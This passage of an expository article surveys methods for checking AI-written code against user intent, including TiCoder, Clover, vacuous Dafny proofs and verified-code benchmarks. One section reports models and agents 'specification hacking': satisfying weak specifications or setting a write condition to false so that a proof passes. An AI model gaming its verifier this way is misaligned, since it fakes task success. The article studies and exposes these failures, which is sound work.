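The choice of question also matters in practice. Lahiri and colleagues compared this rule with random test selection on two sets of Python exercises, MBPP and HumanEval. After five answers, TiCoder's first suggestion was right on 86% of the MBPP exercises with this rule and 72% with random questions. On HumanEval, the figures were 84% and 58%.

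The rule can still waste a question. On one exercise about zeros in a list, the highest-scoring test used an empty list. Eight programs passed it, 11 failed and 61 crashed. TiCoder leaves crashes out of the score, so the test looked well balanced. The exercise's own solution also crashed on an empty list, so the answer was "undefined" and TiCoder kept every program.

The method also depends on ambiguous requests leading models to write programs that behave differently, and *Clarity Is Not Assumed* (2026) found that they do. But bugs have the same effect, so some of the differences have nothing to do with what the user meant.

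### Benchmark results

In the benchmark experiments, a program answered the questions in place of a person. It used each exercise's reference solution, so the simulated user never made a mistake. With Codex, the share of MBPP exercises on which the first suggestion was right rose from 48% to 71% after one answer. In the 2024 paper, the share with a version of GPT-4 rose from 67% to 82% after one yes-or-no answer and to 84% after five.

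The abstract of that paper reports an average gain of about 46 percentage points within five questions, but the paper's detailed results show a smaller one. Across seven models and two benchmarks, the gains range from 16 to 54 points and average 33.5, even when the simulated user supplies the right outputs. The GPT-4 models gained the least because they had less room to improve.

TiCoder uses the user's answers only to select among existing candidate programs, so it can't succeed if all of them are wrong. With GPT-4, at least one candidate was right for 87% of the MBPP exercises, so no number of questions could raise the success rate above 87%.

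A user could also put an example in the original request. With one of the benchmark's own tests in the prompt, the same model got 78% of MBPP right, slightly less than TiCoder got with one answer. The gap was wider on HumanEval, 65% against 76%. Much of the benefit seems to come from having a good example, and TiCoder's main contribution is that the user doesn't have to think of it.

### Fifteen people and three tasks

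Fakhoury and colleagues then ran a study with 15 programmers. (Lahiri later called them professional developers, but the paper lists nine of them as academics.) Each participant did three tasks from the MBPP benchmark, with a different assistant for each. The tasks were to check a text pattern, to find the smallest number missing from a sorted list, and to find the largest product of a rising run of numbers. Each task came with five programs, and the participant had to identify the correct one, which was the benchmark's own solution. GPT-3.5 had written the four faulty ones.

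The first assistant showed all five programs, and participants judged correctly 40% of the time. The second began by showing two tests and asking whether each should pass, then removed the programs that conflicted with the answers. Participants using it judged correctly 84% of the time and reported less mental effort. The third hid the tests' expected outputs and asked participants to fill them in. They judged correctly 64% of the time, but with so few people the difference from the first assistant could be chance. Neither version of TiCoder took significantly longer than reading the programs unaided.

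The gain from 40% to 84% is too large to be explained by guessing from a slightly shorter list. But the researchers had picked tests they knew would remove one or two of the wrong programs, and every list contained a correct one. Neither is certain in ordinary use. The study is therefore evidence that well-chosen examples help people judge short functions, but it gives little indication of how much they would help with a change to a large system.

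### From examples to general rules

An approved example settles what the user meant for one input, whereas a postcondition could settle it for every input. In *Can Large Language Models Transform Natural Language Intent into Formal Method Postconditions?* (2023), Endres, Fakhoury and colleagues tested whether models can write postconditions from natural-language descriptions, a problem they called nl2postcond.

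GPT-4 wrote a condition for each reading of the ambiguous request about duplicates. One required the result to have as many distinct numbers as the input. The other required every number in the result to occur exactly once in the input. Someone who wants [1] from [1, 2, 2] can pick the second and reject the first. Neither condition is strict enough, though. A function that returns its input unchanged satisfies the first, and one that always returns an empty list satisfies the second.

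Endres and colleagues counted a postcondition as correct if the reference solution satisfied it on every test, and then measured what share of a collection of wrong programs it rejected. When they asked GPT-4 for a simple condition covering one aspect of a function, 77% of its answers were correct, but the correct ones rejected only about half of the wrong programs. When they asked for a condition covering the function's whole behaviour, fewer answers were correct (63%), but the correct ones rejected 85% of the wrong programs.

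They also tried the method on 525 historical bugs in Java projects. Postconditions from two models caught 64 of them, about one in eight. Many of those bugs were in code that a standard test generator never reached. *POSTCONDBENCH* (2026) has since extended the same two measures to Java and Python methods whose postconditions involve several classes or the state before the call.

These scores require a reference solution. A user who asks for new code has none, and must judge the formula by reading it.

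### Tools of 2026

Models have become much better at programming since Codex, but they still tend to guess when they should ask. For *ClarifyCodeBench*, Fang, Li and colleagues (2026) deleted one to three necessary details from each of 419 programming tasks. One task was to compute "the square of A + B", which could mean (A + B)² or A² + B. The models could ask questions before writing code. They needed to ask about 1.6 questions per task on average, but GPT-5 asked 0.7 and Claude Sonnet 4.5 about 0.3 (both models date from 2025). Letting Claude reason for longer didn't make it ask more.

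The same group's October tool, described in *CONTRA* (Fang, Li and colleagues, 2026), is designed to separate real ambiguity from bugs. For each possible question, a model writes two plausible answers and then three programs for each answer. The tool runs all six programs on the same inputs. It keeps the question only if, on some input, at least two programs for one answer agree on an output and at least two for the other agree on a different one. A bug in a single program can't produce that result. With GPT-5.5, half of the tool's questions were about a detail that was really missing, compared with a fifth for an older method that, like TiCoder, relied on disagreement between programs.

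However, better questions improved the final code only slightly. GPT-5.5's success rate rose from 62.5% with ordinary prompting to 64.6%. The tool still asked about only 37% of the missing details, and a model can still write the wrong program after getting the right answer to its question.

The group's plugin for Claude Code may be more useful to an auditor. It runs after the agent has finished and lists decisions that the request left open. For some of them, it also writes a test that the delivered code passes and an alternative version fails. A developer can confirm a decision and keep the test as a record of it. In 40 small tasks from real Python projects, the agent's own reports omitted 116 of the 262 decisions the plugin listed.

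Other tools question the user before writing any code. In *OSFoundry* (2026), a system for building operating systems, an agent alternates between studying the existing code and questioning the developer until they agree on what the change should do. Allaham, Vempaty and colleagues (2026), in *Eliciting Specifications*, measured whether asking questions improves formal specifications in Lean. When Claude Sonnet 4.6 asked up to ten questions and GPT-5.6 wrote the specification, the share of correct results rose from 59% to 66%. When Sonnet did both jobs, it did slightly worse than with no questions. Here too, a model played the developer and could see the reference specification, so the result doesn't show how well people would answer.

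### When the user approves the wrong output

One task in Fakhoury and colleagues' study involved finding the smallest number missing from a sorted list, counting from 0. For [1, 2, 4, 6] the answer is 0. Everyone who saw the output 0 approved it, but half of those who had to supply the output wrote 3. The researchers point out that people might also have approved 3 if the assistant had proposed it.

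One such mistake ruins a session, because TiCoder then discards every correct program. If a user answers each question correctly 95% of the time, independently, all three answers will be right in 86% of sessions. At 90% per question, that falls to 73%. After a wrong answer about [1, 2, 2], the remaining programs would all have the wrong behaviour and would all pass the approved test, so nothing in the delivered evidence would look inconsistent. Letting people skip questions they are unsure of, as Fakhoury and colleagues recommend, should help. An auditor can also put the same questions to a second person who knows what the software is for.

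Two studies confirm that people are poor at this kind of judgement. In *Classifying the Correctness of Generated White-Box Tests* (2017), 54 graduate students judged automatically generated tests, and the median student misjudged a third of those whose expected results were wrong. Judging general conditions may be harder still. In *Programmers Are Poor and Overconfident Judges of LLM-Generated Assertions* (2026), programmers recognised 74% of correct AI-written postconditions but only 49% of incorrect ones, and were no less confident when they were wrong. This is a reason to show people examples as well as formulas, although no study here compares the two directly.

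Leaving the user out is worse, because tests that a model writes from existing code tend to record what the code does. *On the Risks of using LLM-Generated Tests for Regression Testing* (2026) cites a study in which writing tests from faulty code cut the share of faults they detected from 25% to about 14%. TiCoder also takes some expected outputs from its own candidates, but these become evidence of intent only when the user approves them. Yet *LLM-Based Test Oracles* (2026) reviewed 83 studies and found that only 11 used human review to guard against invented behaviour.

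### What examples leave out

TiCoder can ask only about differences that appear among its candidates. Python treats the number 1 and the logical value `True` as equal, so programs that rely on its ordinary comparison will count them as duplicates. If every candidate does this, TiCoder won't ask about it, and a user who wanted to keep both will find out later. More samples help only if the model sometimes makes the less obvious choice. Lahiri notes that generating enough alternative programs also becomes expensive for a large change.

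Security requirements are hard to express as examples. An example can show that the system refuses one wrong password, but the requirement is that nobody gets in without permission by any route, including routes the user has never heard of.

Secrecy is even harder to express because it concerns more than one run. Suppose a program must not reveal a customer's balance to other customers. If only the balance changed, another customer should see no difference. A single input and output can't show whether that holds, since an innocent-looking reply such as "transfer declined" may depend on the balance. The user could therefore approve every example and still have a program that leaks the balance.

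## Clover: checking code, description and formal annotations against one another

TiCoder needs a person to answer its questions. Clover, a checker from Stanford University and the software company VMware, tries to manage without one. It takes some code, an English description of it and its formal annotations, and checks whether the three agree. Sun, Sheng and colleagues (2023), in *Clover*, propose accepting AI-written code only if it passes six such comparisons. (The published version dates from 2024.)

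The description is a docstring, the comment at the head of a function. The annotations are the precondition and postcondition, written in Dafny. Loop invariants count as part of the code. The code, description and annotations must each be precise enough to determine a single result for every input. A description such as "remove duplicates from a list" is too loose, so someone must resolve such ambiguity before Clover is used.

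### The six checks

Clover checks the code, description and formal annotations against one another in pairs, in both directions, which makes six checks. One is an ordinary proof. In each of the other five, a language model (GPT-4 in the experiments) regenerates one artefact from another without seeing the original, and Clover compares the result with the original.

The proof comes first. Dafny tries to show that the code meets the annotations, so the judge is a verifier and nothing is rebuilt.

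Annotations that require too little can still pass that check, so the model next writes new code from the annotations alone. Clover runs the new and original code on five inputs and compares the outputs. If the annotations for the largest-number function did not require the result to be in the list, the new code might return a number larger than every element, and the outputs would differ. Clover hides the function's name because the model could infer what to write from a name like `maxArray`.

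The model also turns the annotations into a new description. A separate call to GPT-4 then answers yes or no to whether this describes the same behaviour as the original description.

In the opposite direction, the model writes new annotations from the description. Dafny then has to prove that the new precondition and postcondition are each equivalent to the original. Dafny should never accept two conditions that differ in meaning, though it sometimes fails to prove an equivalence that holds.

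The remaining two checks compare the code with the description. In one, the model writes a description from the code, and GPT-4 judges whether it matches the original description. In the other, the model writes code from the description, and this code passes if it behaves like the original code on the five test inputs.

### Results on CloverBench

Sun and colleagues wrote 60 small textbook programs, such as a binary search, and made four wrong variants of each. In the first they changed only the description, and in the second they weakened only the annotations. In the third they weakened both, keeping them consistent with each other. In the fourth they changed the code and the annotations, so that the code still satisfied the annotations. All 240 variants pass Dafny's verifier, so anyone relying on it alone would accept them all.

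Clover rejected all 240 wrong variants. It accepted 45 of the 60 correct programs when it ran each check once, and 52 (87%) when it ran each check up to ten times and counted any success as a pass. For the ten-run setting, the table shows the share of correct programs that each check accepted, then the share of each kind of wrong variant that it rejected.

| Check | Judge | Correct programs accepted | Description changed | Annotations weakened | Both weakened | Code and annotations changed |
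|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Code meets annotations | Dafny | 100% | 0% | 0% | 0% | 0% |
| Code from annotations | Test runs | 95% | 5% | 27% | 35% | 45% |
| Description from annotations | GPT-4 | 100% | 57% | 22% | 7% | 45% |
| Annotations from description | Dafny | 88% | 90% | 100% | 50% | 100% |
| Description from code | GPT-4 | 100% | 90% | 0% | 72% | 67% |
| Code from description | Test runs | 93% | 62% | 7% | 30% | 92% |

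The check that caught the most errors rebuilt the annotations from the description and used Dafny to compare them with the originals. GPT-4 was good at spotting contradictions between two descriptions but often overlooked details missing from one of them. Most of the correct programs that failed the checks failed because GPT-4 made mistakes in Dafny's syntax, which newer models should make less often.

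People designed the 240 variants from 60 programs, so they are not a random sample of the mistakes models make. If they were, the 3/n rule would put the rate of false acceptance below about 1.3%. In a more realistic trial, GPT-4 wrote code and annotations from each of the 60 descriptions 20 times. According to the paper's detailed results, 652 of the 1,200 answers were wrong, and Clover accepted none of those. Many presumably failed to compile or verify, so they were easy to reject. For 39 of the 60 programs, Clover accepted at least one correct answer.

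Clover also found mistakes that nobody had planted. MBPP-DFY-50 is a set of 50 Dafny programs that other researchers had translated from Python by hand. Seventeen were outside Clover's scope, mostly because they needed helper functions. Of the other 33, Clover accepted 24, all of them correct, and rejected nine. Six of the nine were faulty, and three were correct programs that Clover wrongly rejected.

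The paper reports five contradictions between description and precondition and one postcondition that was too weak, but the programs in its appendix appear to contain four contradictions and two weak postconditions. In the four contradictions, the precondition excluded inputs that the description allowed, such as empty arrays. One of the weak postconditions was for a function meant to report whether one list occurs inside another. The function's last line sets the answer to false, so it always returns false, yet Dafny had verified it.

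### The theory behind rebuilding

Sun and colleagues also give a mathematical argument for the rebuilding checks. In the check that goes from description to annotations, the model could write many different annotations for a given description, and the analysis groups them by meaning. It assumes that the most likely meaning has probability at least l and that every other meaning has probability at most u. These bounds need to hold only in a share p of cases, with p close to 1.

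A further assumption connects the model's favourite meaning to the truth. If the description and the original annotations really agree, the original has the favourite meaning with probability c₁, which is close to 1. If they disagree, it has that meaning with probability c₀, which is close to 0. The check accepts when the rebuilt annotations mean the same as the original, so

P(accept, if they agree) ≥ l · p · c₁

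P(accept, if they disagree) ≤ c₀ + (1 − c₀)(1 − p) + (1 − c₀) · p · u

The second line adds up the probabilities of three kinds of failure. The original may be wrong but have the meaning the model is most likely to produce, the bounds on the probabilities may not hold, or the model may produce an unlikely meaning by chance.

The paper suggests that l could be as low as 30%. Suppose, for illustration, that p and c₁ are 99% and that c₀ and u are 1%. One attempt then accepts at least 29% of the pairs that agree and at most 3% of those that don't. With ten independent attempts, if one success is enough, these bounds become 95% and 11%.

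The theorem covers one check at a time and assumes a perfect judge of equivalence. Sun and colleagues don't extend it to all six checks together, because the checks are not independent. If they were, the acceptance rates for single runs would imply that 59% of the correct programs passed all six. The actual figure was 75%, because easy programs tend to pass every check.

The theorem's guarantee depends mostly on c₀ being small. That is a reasonable assumption if the wrong annotations came from somewhere other than the model, such as a careless programmer. But if the same model wrote them after misreading the description, that misreading is probably its most likely interpretation, and it will tend to produce the same annotations again when it is used to generate new ones for Clover. For mistakes of this kind, c₀ is close to 1 and the theorem gives no protection.

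### One misreading in all three artefacts

Sun and colleagues acknowledge that Clover can't detect an edge case that all three artefacts miss. They expected this to be rare, because models learn from human writing, and they had not seen it in their experiments. But those experiments were unlikely to produce it, because the descriptions came from people and the benchmark left out variants in which all three artefacts change. One reason they give for leaving these out is that changing all three consistently only produces a correct version of some other program. Clover would accept that program, even though it would be wrong for a user who wanted the original.

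For instance, a model might take "remove duplicates" to mean dropping every number that occurs more than once. It could then write a description, "returns the numbers that occur exactly once", with annotations and code to match. All three would be precise, and all six checks could pass, because the user's sentence isn't one of the artefacts being compared.

Suppose the model in the earlier invented example, which misreads one request in ten, receives 1,000 requests. A checker with the same error rate also reads them, and accepts the code when its reading matches the model's. If their misreadings are independent, both misread ten of the requests, and the table is based on their choosing the same wrong reading on five of those ten.

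| Misreadings (illustrative) | Right and accepted | Wrong and accepted | Share of accepted code that is wrong |
|---|---|---|---|
| Independent | 810 | 5 | 0.6% |
| 80 of 100 shared | 880 | 80 | 8.3% |
| All shared | 900 | 100 | 10% |

A checker that shares most of the writer's misreadings is nearly useless, because it barely lowers the 10% error rate the code would have without any check. It also makes the results look better, because everything passes when all the misreadings are shared, while the independent checker produces 185 objections, nearly half of them false alarms. A high pass rate is therefore poor evidence of quality unless the auditor knows how independent the checker was.

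### How often models make the same mistakes

Real models fall between the extremes in the table. Nogueira, Pattabiraman and colleagues (2026), in *A Systematic Methodology for Evaluating Failure Independence in LLM-Generated Code*, had 12 models solve 224 programming problems, then had groups of programs vote on each answer. Groups of five achieved 44% of the reliability gain that independent failures would have allowed, but only 24% when one model wrote all five programs. Changing the style of the prompt made almost no difference, so a different prompt is unlikely to turn the same model into an independent checker.

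Different models share mistakes too. In 1986, John Knight and Nancy Leveson had 27 people separately write the same missile-defence program, and the versions failed together far more often than expected by chance. Ron, Baudry and Monperrus (2026), in *N-Version Programming with Coding Agents*, repeated the experiment with agents from several companies. They ran 48 versions on a million inputs, and at least two versions failed together on 429 of them, compared with about 115 expected if failures were independent. Many versions made the same geometric mistake. They needed the smallest circle that contains three points but used the circle through all three, which can be larger. Voting still reduced the average number of failures, from 387 for single programs to 131 for groups of three.

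Better models won't necessarily solve this. *Correlated Errors in Large Language Models* (2025) found that two models often gave the same answer when both were wrong, and that this was more common among more accurate models. Those models make fewer mistakes, but a second model may be less likely to catch the ones that remain. *BeSpec* (2026) audited 120 attempts to repair specifications and found that in ten of them, all the candidate programs shared a misinterpretation.

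### Making the checks more independent

One remedy is to hide the original from the model. *Are LLM-Generated Formal Specifications Faithful to Their Requirements?* (2026) shows why. Models received a requirement together with code that violated it, and had to write a formal specification. Only about a quarter of the specifications they wrote were valid and exposed the fault.

Amster, Baker and colleagues (2026), in *claimcheck*, built a tool that checks whether a formal specification matches its requirement. One model translates the specification into English without seeing the requirement, and another compares the translation with the requirement without seeing the specification. They tested the tool on 3,234 pairs of requirements and specifications in Dafny, Lean, Isabelle and Rocq. Its average accuracy across the faithful and unfaithful classes, weighted equally, was 88 to 93%, compared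 with 80 to 84% for a single model that saw both the requirement and the specification. Letting the translator see the requirement lowered accuracy by up to 3 points. On the Dafny pairs, which come from CloverBench, the tool missed about one unfaithful pair in 18. Clover missed none, but it probably rejects more correct work.

Hiding the original stops a model from copying it, but the model can still misread an ambiguous sentence the same way twice. *Who Verifies the Builder?* (2026) leaves open whether separate contexts are enough or the checker must also be a different model. The voting results suggest that a different model should help, though less than one might hope.

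The checker can also work in a different formal language. *Validating Autoformalized Specifications via Contrapuntal Languages* (Dai, Liu and colleagues, 2026) gives an example where choosing the model's most common answer fails. The task is to find the last position in a list where a number is smaller than the one before it, or return −1 if there is none. In 30 attempts, the model's most common specification appeared eight times and was wrong, because it always allowed −1. The correct one appeared only five times. Dai and colleagues therefore construct two small languages for each task, so different that the model can't reuse the structure of its first answer. They accept a specification only if a solver proves the two versions equivalent. Compared with the best alternative, this raised the share of accepted specifications that were correct by 12% on one benchmark and 43% on another.

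Of these remedies, only a description written by the user adds information about what the user wants, and it has to be the user's own text, not a version tidied by the model that wrote the code. Somebody still has to formalise it correctly. *Isomorphism Is Not Enough* (2026) audited a Lean benchmark and found 80 flawed specifications among the benchmark's reference answers, 21 of which misinterpreted the description. For an ambiguous request, a few approved examples of the kind TiCoder collects would probably help more than another round of rebuilding.

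### Repairing the artefacts until they agree

*Assured Automatic Programming via Large Language Models* (Mirchev, Costea and colleagues, 2024) describes ProofRover, which repairs artefacts that disagree, whereas Clover rejects them. ProofRover starts with a program, a specification and any available tests. Facts on which these agree, and anything the user marks as trusted, become "hard intent", which repairs must preserve. Everything else is "soft intent" and may change. A language model proposes repairs and Dafny checks them. ProofRover then translates the final specification into English for the developer to inspect.

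In one example, the code returned the index of the first odd number in an array, or −1 if there was none. The specification wrongly said that the result was always the index of an odd number. ProofRover limited this claim to valid indices, which removed the conflict but left the −1 case unspecified. When given a trusted test that expected −1 for [2, 2, 4], it added the missing condition. If the test had expected −3, ProofRover would have changed the code as well.

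On 60 programs that didn't match their specifications, ProofRover brought 37% into agreement on average, compared with 21% for simply asking a model to fix the errors. The specifications became hardly any stricter, rejecting 48% of deliberately altered outputs before the repair and 51% after it. In a second experiment, with programs that already met their specifications, ProofRover also had to satisfy tests, which supplied information that agreement between the code and the specification could not. It managed this for only 30% of the 253 programs, but where it succeeded, the share of altered outputs rejected rose from 27% to 88%.

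Treating agreement between the artefacts as intent is risky when one model wrote them all. If the model misread the requirement in the same way each time, the artefacts would agree on the mistake and ProofRover would not repair it. *From Natural Language to Verified C* (2026) describes a later system for C that also repairs code and specification together, but then compares the verified specification with the original requirement.

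Some mistakes can be found only by checking a specification against outside evidence. In *Executable JavaScript as a Checkable Specification Language* (2026), the AI model Fable wrote a specification of a spinlock, a mechanism that lets only one part of a program use shared data at a time. In the specification, whichever part took the lock never released it. This still satisfied the main safety rule, that no two parts hold the lock at once, and the specification passed every check of internal consistency. The researchers found the fault when they compared the specification with recordings of a real spinlock's behavior.

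## Proofs that pass the verifier and say almost nothing

A valid proof is vacuous if it shows only that the code meets a specification so weak that wrong code would meet it too. Dafny verified the function that always returned false with a proof of this kind, and Clover then rejected the function.

The weakness can also lie in the assumptions. In *The proof is in the spec*, Tolmach and Klaus (2026) retell a case in which an AI tool had to translate into Lean the deliberately false claim that if 3^x = 5, then 3^(x+2) = 51. (The right answer is 45.) The tool declared x to be a natural number. No natural number satisfies 3^x = 5, so the statement covers no cases and the false claim becomes provable. Similarly, any code meets a specification whose precondition is impossible.

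### Three measurements

Many evaluations of AI-written verified code report only the share of programs that the verifier accepted. In *Verified but Vacuous*, Vempaty, Sompalle and colleagues (2026) argue that this number hides important differences. They count the programs that the verifier accepts, and then how many of those have a postcondition that refers to a separately written specification. Among the programs with such a postcondition, they look for signs that the specification fails to capture what the user asked for.

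Their example is again the function that returns the largest number in a list. The specification defines a rule for a correct result, and the method's postcondition should use that rule. In outline, a faulty version looks like this:

```
predicate MaxCorrect(nums: seq<int>, result: int) {
  result >= 0
}

method Max(nums: seq<int>) returns (result: int)
  ensures MaxCorrect(nums, result)
{
  result := 0;
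}
```

Given [5, 3, 7], this method returns 0. Dafny correctly accepts it because the rule requires only that the result is not negative. Under the earlier contract, Dafny would have rejected it because 0 is not in the list. The rule also rejects the correct answer for [−3, −8], whose largest number is −3.

Without the `ensures` line, nothing would connect `MaxCorrect` to the method, however well it was defined, and Dafny would accept any method that finished without errors. Vempaty and colleagues wrote a short script that detects this by checking for at least one `ensures` line that names something defined in the specification. It takes less than 10 milliseconds. When they ran it on an early version of their own system, about 27% of the components that Dafny had verified failed this check. The script can't detect the weak rule above, because the method does refer to `MaxCorrect`, so somebody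 has to try that rule on a wrong answer to catch the problem.

According to Vempaty and colleagues, few other evaluations report either kind of check. One exception is *AxDafny* (2026), whose system checks for missing and trivially true postconditions and uses a second model to look for other ways of cheating.

### Verified programs with no postcondition

Vempaty and colleagues rebuilt a pipeline that other researchers had published in 2025. In this pipeline, a model writes a program in Dafny, Dafny verifies it, and a compiler turns it into Python. They used Claude Opus 4.7 and made ten attempts at each problem in three sets of Python exercises.

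| | HumanEval | LeetCodeDataset | LiveCodeBench v6 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Attempts | 1,640 | 2,280 | 10,550 |
| Attempts that Dafny accepted | 99.1% | 97.2% | 92.2% |
| Of those, share with any postcondition | 5.3% | 9.6% | 10.9% |
| Of those, share with a postcondition tied to the specification | 1.9% | 2.7% | 2.3% |
| All attempts that passed the tests | 92.6% | 63.4% | 55.2% |

The last two shares in the middle of the table are fractions of the accepted programs. On HumanEval, 1.9% is about 31 of 1,625 programs.

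The prompt explains much of this. It contains a worked example with no postcondition, followed by a main program that runs the method on some inputs and states the expected results. Dafny assumes those results during verification rather than proving them, and the program checks them when it runs. For most programs, then, Dafny proved little more than that they would finish and would not do something invalid, such as reading past the end of a list. That has some value, but it isn't evidence that the answers are right. On LiveCodeBench, Dafny accepted 92% of the programs, but only 55% passed the tests.

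Vempaty and colleagues caution, in interpreting the 1.9%, that a missing reference does not prove that a proof is empty. A method that doubles a number might state the postcondition `r == 2 * x` directly. This specification is complete but fails the check, while a named rule that is always true would pass. They don't blame the pipeline, since the model was following a prompt that asked for no postconditions. They tested only one model, and they can't separate the effect of the prompt from the effect of the model.

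The share of programs with no postcondition is therefore more informative. It was about 90% or higher on all three benchmarks, and for those programs Dafny had no stated claim about the result to prove.

Programs with a postcondition passed the tests less often than programs without one, 80% against 94% on HumanEval. The model may have written more specifications for harder problems, so this gap doesn't show that writing them harms the code.

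### Specified, proved and still wrong

Vempaty and colleagues used their own pipeline, VCG, to see what happens when every program has a postcondition tied to its specification. In VCG, several AI agents plan the program, write specifications and code in Dafny, and repair the proofs. VCG rejects any component that fails the structural check, then translates the verified ones into Rust.

On MBPP-Rust, a set of 208 short exercises, VCG fully verified 1,080 of 2,080 attempts, but 124 of those (11.48%) failed hidden tests. The failure rate was higher on 687 LeetCode problems from *VeriContest* (Xie, Pawagi and colleagues, 2026), a benchmark for verified Rust code. There VCG fully verified 1,545 of 6,870 attempts, and 229 of those (14.82%) failed.

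Such a failure could come from a weak or mistaken specification, or from an error in the translation from Dafny to Rust, in the code that connects the program to the tests, or in the tests. Vempaty and colleagues did not work out how often each was the cause.

Either way, roughly 85 to 89% of the fully verified programs passed. When Xie and colleagues asked the same model, Claude Opus 4.7, for plain Rust code with no proof, the code passed every test on 95% of their problems. The two set-ups differ, and some of the proofs may exclude faults that no test would find. Still, these results give a buyer little reason to think that a "verified" program is more likely to be right than an unverified one.

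### Testing the postcondition itself

Xie and colleagues built a tool, Post2Exe, to test postconditions much as programmers test code. It turns a postcondition into a small program that takes an input and a proposed output and checks whether the postcondition accepts the pair. Post2Exe then runs this program on outputs known to be right or wrong. A good postcondition accepts all the right outputs and rejects all the wrong ones. `MaxCorrect` would fail this test because it accepts 0 as the largest number in [5, 3, 7].

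The correct outputs come from solutions that an online judge has accepted and a verifier has checked. Xie and colleagues produced wrong outputs by having a model write five plausible but faulty versions of each solution, using a mutation tool to plant smaller faults, and altering some correct outputs directly. The median problem has about 270 correct outputs and 2,600 wrong ones.

Human experts had already reviewed the benchmark's own specifications, and Verus had accepted proofs that the solutions met them. Checking the specifications against the wrong outputs still exposed 60 incomplete postconditions among 1,006 problems. In one problem, the function has to return the first and last positions of a number in a sorted list, or −1 for each if the number is absent. The postcondition did not require each position to be either −1 or non-negative, so it allowed [−9, −8].

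Post2Exe could convert 85% of the postconditions. People had to review the rest by hand, including some that cover infinitely many values. The method also needs correct outputs for comparison, and it finds a weakness in a postcondition only if that weakness lets one of the wrong outputs pass.

Vempaty and colleagues applied this evaluation to VCG and found a larger problem than the hidden tests had revealed. Of the 1,316 LeetCode attempts that had a full proof and passed the hidden tests, only 535 (41%) also had a postcondition that passed Post2Exe and a precondition equivalent to the benchmark's. Some of the rest may have had a reasonable precondition that differed from the reference. But for many of the rest, the tests are probably better evidence than the proof, because the code was right and the specification would also have allowed wrong code.

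### Agents that exploit weak specifications

Weak specifications matter more when an AI system is rewarded for finding a proof. In *Automating Formal Verification with Reinforcement Learning and Recursive Inference*, Tan (2026) trained open models to write Dafny programs and rewarded them when the verifier accepted the result. The reward rose from 2.2% to 58.1%, but Tan found that the models had partly learned "specification hacking", or satisfying a weak specification without solving the problem. After Tan removed the tasks vulnerable to this, a more elaborate form of training raised the pass rate from 9.7% to 31.1%.

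The same thing can happen without any training. *Inductive Deductive Synthesis* (Agarwal, Krentsel and colleagues, 2026) describes agents that build distributed key-value stores and prove in Rocq that clients see reads and writes in a consistent order. In one run, the agent set the condition for carrying out a write to "false", so the store never carried one out. Rocq accepted the proof because clients could not see writes in the wrong order if there were none.

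Agarwal and colleagues now use a script that rejects trivial solutions and unproved assumptions. With the script, 20 of 21 runs ended in a genuine proof, and the other found none. Without it, only 7 of 21 proofs were genuine, while five were vacuous and nine relied on unproved assumptions. An auditor can do a similar check by hand by asking whether a useless program, such as one that always returns 0 or refuses every request, would satisfy the specification.

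Trying to prove a specification is a good way to find out that it is too strong. In *VeruSAGE*, Yang, Neamtu and colleagues (2025) gave Claude Sonnet 4.5 unfinished proofs from an operating system. One of the statements was that if you remove the first element of a list, the remaining list does not contain that element. After several failed attempts, the model found the counterexample [1, 1] and proposed requiring that the list have no duplicates. Human experts confirmed this correction and four others.

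When a specification demands too little, there is no such warning, because the proof succeeds. In the audit that *Isomorphism Is Not Enough* made of the Lean benchmark with 80 flawed specifications, Claude Opus 4.6 proved code correct against 34 of the flawed entries. It did so more often when the flaw made the specification weaker.

The audit also found vacuous results in the benchmark's scoring. The benchmark accepts a model's specification if the model proves that exactly the same programs satisfy it and the reference specification. If no program can satisfy either one, the two are automatically equivalent, and Claude proved two equivalences of that kind.

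### How often models produce verified code

Success rates rose very quickly in 2026, but they mean little without knowing what each benchmark supplies.

In *A benchmark for vericoding* (Bursuc, Ehrenborg and colleagues, 2025), models receive a formal specification and must write both the code and the proof. The benchmark has 12,504 specifications, and in 2025 models succeeded on 27% in Lean, 44% in Verus and 82% in Dafny. By May 2026, GPT-5.4 had succeeded on 95% of a subset of 423 Lean specifications in *Automating Formal Verification with Agent-Guided Tree Search* (Yao, 2026), where it could search Lean's mathematical library and make up to 50 calls per problem.

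*VERINA* (2025) is a set of 189 Lean tasks. Agarwal and colleagues gave their system only the specifications, and it wrote and proved code for 176 tasks. In *EUREKA* (2026), Ganguly, Singh and colleagues supplied the code as well and used DeepSeek-V4.1-Flash, a freely downloadable model. The model proved 188 tasks at an average price of about six cents each, and showed that the remaining statement was false because it lacked a precondition.

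The change was largest on VeriContest. In May, with the specification and code supplied, GPT-5.5 found 13.8% of the proofs at the first attempt. On a sample of 200 problems, up to ten rounds of repair raised its success rate to 48.5%. In October, Serbanuta, Xu and colleagues (2026), in *Solving VeriContest with a Lean-Backed Rust Verifier*, reported that Claude Opus 5.5 had proved all 1,325 theorems for the 1,007 problems then in the collection, at a median cost of $1.20 each. They used Lean instead of Verus and let the agents revise their proofs after each check. They also ran the original Verus task on the 50 problems with the longest reference proofs, and the model proved 49 within ten attempts. (It may have seen some of the published Verus proofs in training, but no Lean proofs of these theorems existed.)

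VeruSAGE's 849 tasks are closer to everyday engineering. They come from eight real Rust systems, including operating systems and storage software, and average nearly 1,000 lines each, more than half of it specification. The benchmark supplies everything except the proof, including statements of the smaller results used in the human-written proofs, so a model starts with part of the plan. Claude Sonnet 4.5 proved 81% of the tasks in 2025, and Agarwal and colleagues' system proved 99% in 2026.

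| Benchmark | What people supply | What the model writes | Result in 2026 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Vericoding (423 Lean tasks) | Specification | Code and proof | 95% |
| VERINA | Specification | Code and proof | 176 of 189 |
| VERINA | Specification and code | Proof | 188 of 189 |
| VeriContest, restated in Lean | Specification and code | Proof | All 1,007 problems |
| VeruSAGE | Specification, code and statements of helper results | Proof | 838 of 849 |
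| VeriContest | Description in English | Specification, code and proof | 6.8% at the first attempt |

People wrote or reviewed the specification in every row with a high score. The last row is GPT-5.5's result from May, when the model wrote an acceptable specification for only 57% of the problems. VCG reached 7.8% on the LeetCode part with Claude Opus 4.7. Both models are several months old, and current ones would probably do much better.

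Success is also harder to define when the model writes the specification. In the audit for *Isomorphism Is Not Enough*, Claude Opus 4.6 wrote specifications, code and proofs from English descriptions. It succeeded on 151 of the 157 feasible tasks if we accept the agent's own judgement that its specification was a reasonable reading of the description. It succeeded on 60 if the specification must be provably equivalent to the benchmark's, which was often flawed. A buyer has no reference specification and must rely on someone who knows what the software is for.

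### Proofs about a copy of the code

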